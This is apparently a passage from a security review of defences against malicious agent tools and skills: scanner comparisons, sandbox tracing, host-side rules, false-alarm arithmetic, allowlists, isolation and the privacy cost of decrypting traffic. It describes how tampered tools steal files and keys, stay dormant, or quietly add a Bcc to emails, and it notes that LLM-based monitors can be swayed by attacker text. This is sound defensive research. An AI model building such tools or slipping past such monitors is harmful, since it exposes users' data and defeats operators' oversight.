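The table compares Cisco's scanner, which uses a language model to read code as well as descriptions, with Bandit, a general checker for risky Python code. In the last column, a tool counts as flagged if any of six scanners flagged it.

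| | Cisco | Bandit | Any of six scanners |
|---|---|---|---|
| Caught: sends a local file to an outsider | 80% | 87% | 93% |
| Caught: downloads a program from an attacker | 80% | 94% | 95% |
| Caught: deletes local files | 45% | 86% | 86% |
| Caught: encrypts local files | 6% | 69% | over 99% |
| False alarms on clean code repositories | 0.6% | 63% | 66% |

Cisco's scanner caught four in five of the file thefts with very few false alarms, but it caught almost nothing in the ShieldNet study. In that study, the scanner may have had access only to the tool definitions, or the attacks may have been harder to recognise. Most of the tools Hu and colleagues collected had fewer than 100 lines of code, which also makes an inserted function easier to spot.

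Bandit's results are much less useful. It flagged 63% of the clean repositories, so it would have flagged many of the tampered tools even without the malicious code. Two of the researchers examined 200 tools from the clean set that at least one scanner had flagged, and found nothing malicious.

ShieldNet does not detect purely local harms, as its developers acknowledge. A tool that deletes the user's files without using the network produces no traffic to classify. A log on the host machine would show the deletion, but a person or program would still have to judge whether the user wanted it.

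### Watching the machine as well as the network

Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil Wears Markdown*, measured what host-side evidence adds to a scan. They had an agent try out each skill in a sandbox for up to five minutes while they recorded system calls, file changes and network traffic. The agent skipped dangerous steps and noted what the skill had told it to do. A group of language models then judged the skill from different combinations of evidence. The test set had 80 malicious skills and 60 presumed harmless ones:

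| Evidence given to the models | Malicious skills caught | Harmless skills flagged | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| The skill's files | 54 of 80 | 21 of 60 | 0.70 |
| Files and matches from scanning rules | 28 of 80 | 3 of 60 | 0.50 |
| Files and sandbox records | 63 of 80 | 5 of 60 | 0.85 |
| All three | 68 of 80 | 5 of 60 | 0.89 |

Flagging all 140 skills as malicious would have scored 0.73, slightly more than the models scored with the files alone. The sandbox records made the largest difference, helping the models catch more malicious skills and raise fewer false alarms. The scanning rules alone made the models flag too few skills.

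The observed false positive rate of 8% is based on only 60 harmless skills, so the true rate could be well above or below that. Truong-Le and colleagues also didn't independently verify all the skills they had labelled harmless, and they warn that a single sandbox run can miss behaviour.

A larger study suggests that malicious skills often stay inactive during a short test. Liu and colleagues confirmed 157 malicious skills, but another 4,130 suspicious ones did nothing harmful during a 60-second run. They reviewed 413 of these by hand, reading the skills without seeing any attacks run, and judged 93% to be dormant malware, set to activate on a certain date, on a certain kind of machine or in a later session. If that share is right for all 4,130, the registries held about 3,850 dormant malicious skills, roughly 25 for each confirmed one.

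Other results on sandboxes are harder to generalise. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026) reports that running nine deliberately vulnerable servers revealed a problem in all nine, while static analysis found problems in two. But the static analyser couldn't process JavaScript properly, and all seven servers it missed were written in JavaScript.

Host-side monitoring can also continue while an agent is in use. *AgentSpy* (2026) presents a system that records system calls and network traffic from the agent and every program it starts, and applies fixed rules to the system calls. A rule might forbid a text-formatting tool from opening an SSH key. The same calls always produce the same result, and text written by an attacker can't suppress an alarm, as it might if a language model checked the calls. Nobody seems to have tested AgentSpy or a similar recorder on SC-Inject-Bench,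 so there is no direct comparison with ShieldNet.

### Eighty false alarms for one attack

A false positive rate of 0.8% sounds low, but attacks are rare in normal use. Suppose a company's agents make 10,000 tool calls a day and one of them is malicious:

9,999 × 0.008 ≈ 80 false alarms

ShieldNet would probably also catch the malicious call, so the security team would get about 81 alarms, one of them for a real attack. At ten minutes per alarm, investigating them all would take the team more than 13 hours a day.

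In general, if a share m of calls is malicious, r is the detector's recall and f is its false positive rate, the share of alarms that are real is

r × m / (r × m + f × (1 − m))

With r = 0.99 and f = 0.008, this gives:

| Share of calls that are malicious | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|
| 95%, as in the test | almost 100% |
| 50% | 99% |
| 1% | 56% |
| 0.1% | 11% |
| 0.01%, as in the example | 1.2% |

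The false positive rate would have to fall to 0.01% to bring the example down to one false alarm a day. The rate in practice could be higher than 0.8%, because the researchers measured it in a laboratory, using scripted requests to fewer than a thousand clean tools.

Real computers produce a lot of harmless traffic that looks suspicious. *PocketAgents* (2026) gives the examples of an update service that resembles an attacker's control channel and a scheduled backup that resembles data theft. A monitor can use a list of such services to avoid repeating the same false alarms. The security team can also combine repeated alarms about one tool into a single investigation.

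Another option is to require a second kind of evidence, such as an alarm from a host-side rule. If that rule independently flags 1% of harmless calls, requiring both alarms would reduce the 80 false alarms to about one a day. The two signals are unlikely to be fully independent, since a backup both reads many files and sends a lot of data. Requiring both would also miss `postmark-mcp`, which opened no suspicious files.

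A high false positive rate is easier to tolerate in a check that runs once per release than in one that runs on every call. At the 8% rate above, sandbox testing of 1,000 new skills would flag about 80 harmless ones, which a person would need to review once, and again only if the skills changed. Checking 10,000 calls a day at the same rate would produce 800 false alarms daily.

### Allowlists of destinations

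With an allowlist, the operator lists the outside addresses that a tool needs and the network blocks everything else, so traffic doesn't have to be classified. The LiteLLM malware sent stolen data to `models.litellm.cloud`. That address would not have been on a list of genuine model providers, so an allowlist would have blocked the theft even before anyone had recognised the malware.

*Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) recommends blocking all network access, then allowing specific hostnames rather than IP addresses, because the addresses change. It gives sandboxes that run code no outside access by default. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a design for healthcare, gives each type of agent its own short allowlist and logs every refused connection. The log is a useful alarm because a tool with a complete allowlist has little reason to try other destinations.

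Lists of allowed domains for general programming work are much longer. *Permission Denied* (2026), a test of coding agents, allowed 205 domains and forced the agents' child processes through the same proxy. An attacker may be able to open an account at one of the permitted services and have the data sent there. `postmark-mcp` sent data out through the one service that the tool needed.

More specific rules reduce this problem. *Avalon-M1* (2026) describes a proxy whose rules cover the path and the type of request as well as the host. For an invented weather tool, such a policy might be:

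```
allow  GET  api.weather.example/forecast/*
deny   everything else
```

The tool can request a forecast but can't upload a file. A malicious version could still hide a password in the city name if the attacker could read the weather service's records.

The same proxy has an audit mode, which logs the requests a policy would block but lets them through. This helps an operator find entries missing from the list before enforcing it. Someone still has to review the logged addresses, because a tool that is already compromised will contact the attacker during the trial, and an operator who approves every address will approve the attacker's too.

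Operators also need to test that the restriction works. *Sandman* (2026), a report on a sandbox service, describes a live check in which all six sandboxes labelled as having no outside access could reach the internet. The software that created them had not installed the network rules. Operators could detect this failure in seconds by trying to open a forbidden address from inside each sandbox.

### What a sandbox adds

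A sandbox limits the local harm that an allowlist can't prevent. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) advises running servers without administrator rights and with access only to their working folder. A malicious server could still damage the files in that folder.

Containers share the host's kernel, so a flaw in it can let code escape from any container. *Tracekit Box* (2026) instead runs each job in its own small virtual machine. It also keeps credentials out of the sandbox. The agent's code gets only a placeholder, and a proxy on the host inserts the real key into requests to approved addresses. Under this setup, a malicious email server could not have stolen the Postmark key, but it could still have added a Bcc to each message.

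Isolation can't make a tool's answers trustworthy either. *TrustShiftProbe* (2026) points out that a malicious server can return manipulated data without exceeding its permissions. A sandboxed price-comparison tool could recommend the attacker's shop every time while visiting only the websites it is supposed to.

### The cost of decrypting traffic

ShieldNet needs to decrypt traffic to keep false alarms low, but decryption exposes private data. The Kolkata recording contains the user's request in plain text, including the remark that they needed to schedule a call. It also contains the tool's reply, because the agent sends that to the model provider over the same connection. ShieldNet therefore has access to much of what an action log contains, even though its developers describe it as working from network behaviour alone. A proxy that intercepted all traffic could also expose someone's email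 or online banking if they used the same machine for those.

The proxy is also a target for attackers. Programs accept it only because the machine trusts certificates that the proxy issues, so an attacker who steals the proxy's signing key, and can get between the machine and the internet, could imitate almost any website to that machine. A program that accepts only its own provider's certificate will not connect through the proxy, so the operator has to exempt the program from inspection or do without it.

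Operators can limit the exposure of decrypted traffic by intercepting only traffic from the sandbox where the agent's tools run, and by deleting recordings soon after classifying them. ShieldNet's model is small enough to run on an operator's own hardware, so the decrypted traffic doesn't have to go to an outside company. Rules about paths and request types require decryption, but an allowlist of hostnames usually doesn't, because a program normally reveals the site's name when it opens an encrypted connection. An operator could therefore filter by hostname alone for most tools and decrypt traffic only for those that handle valuable data or need access to many sites.
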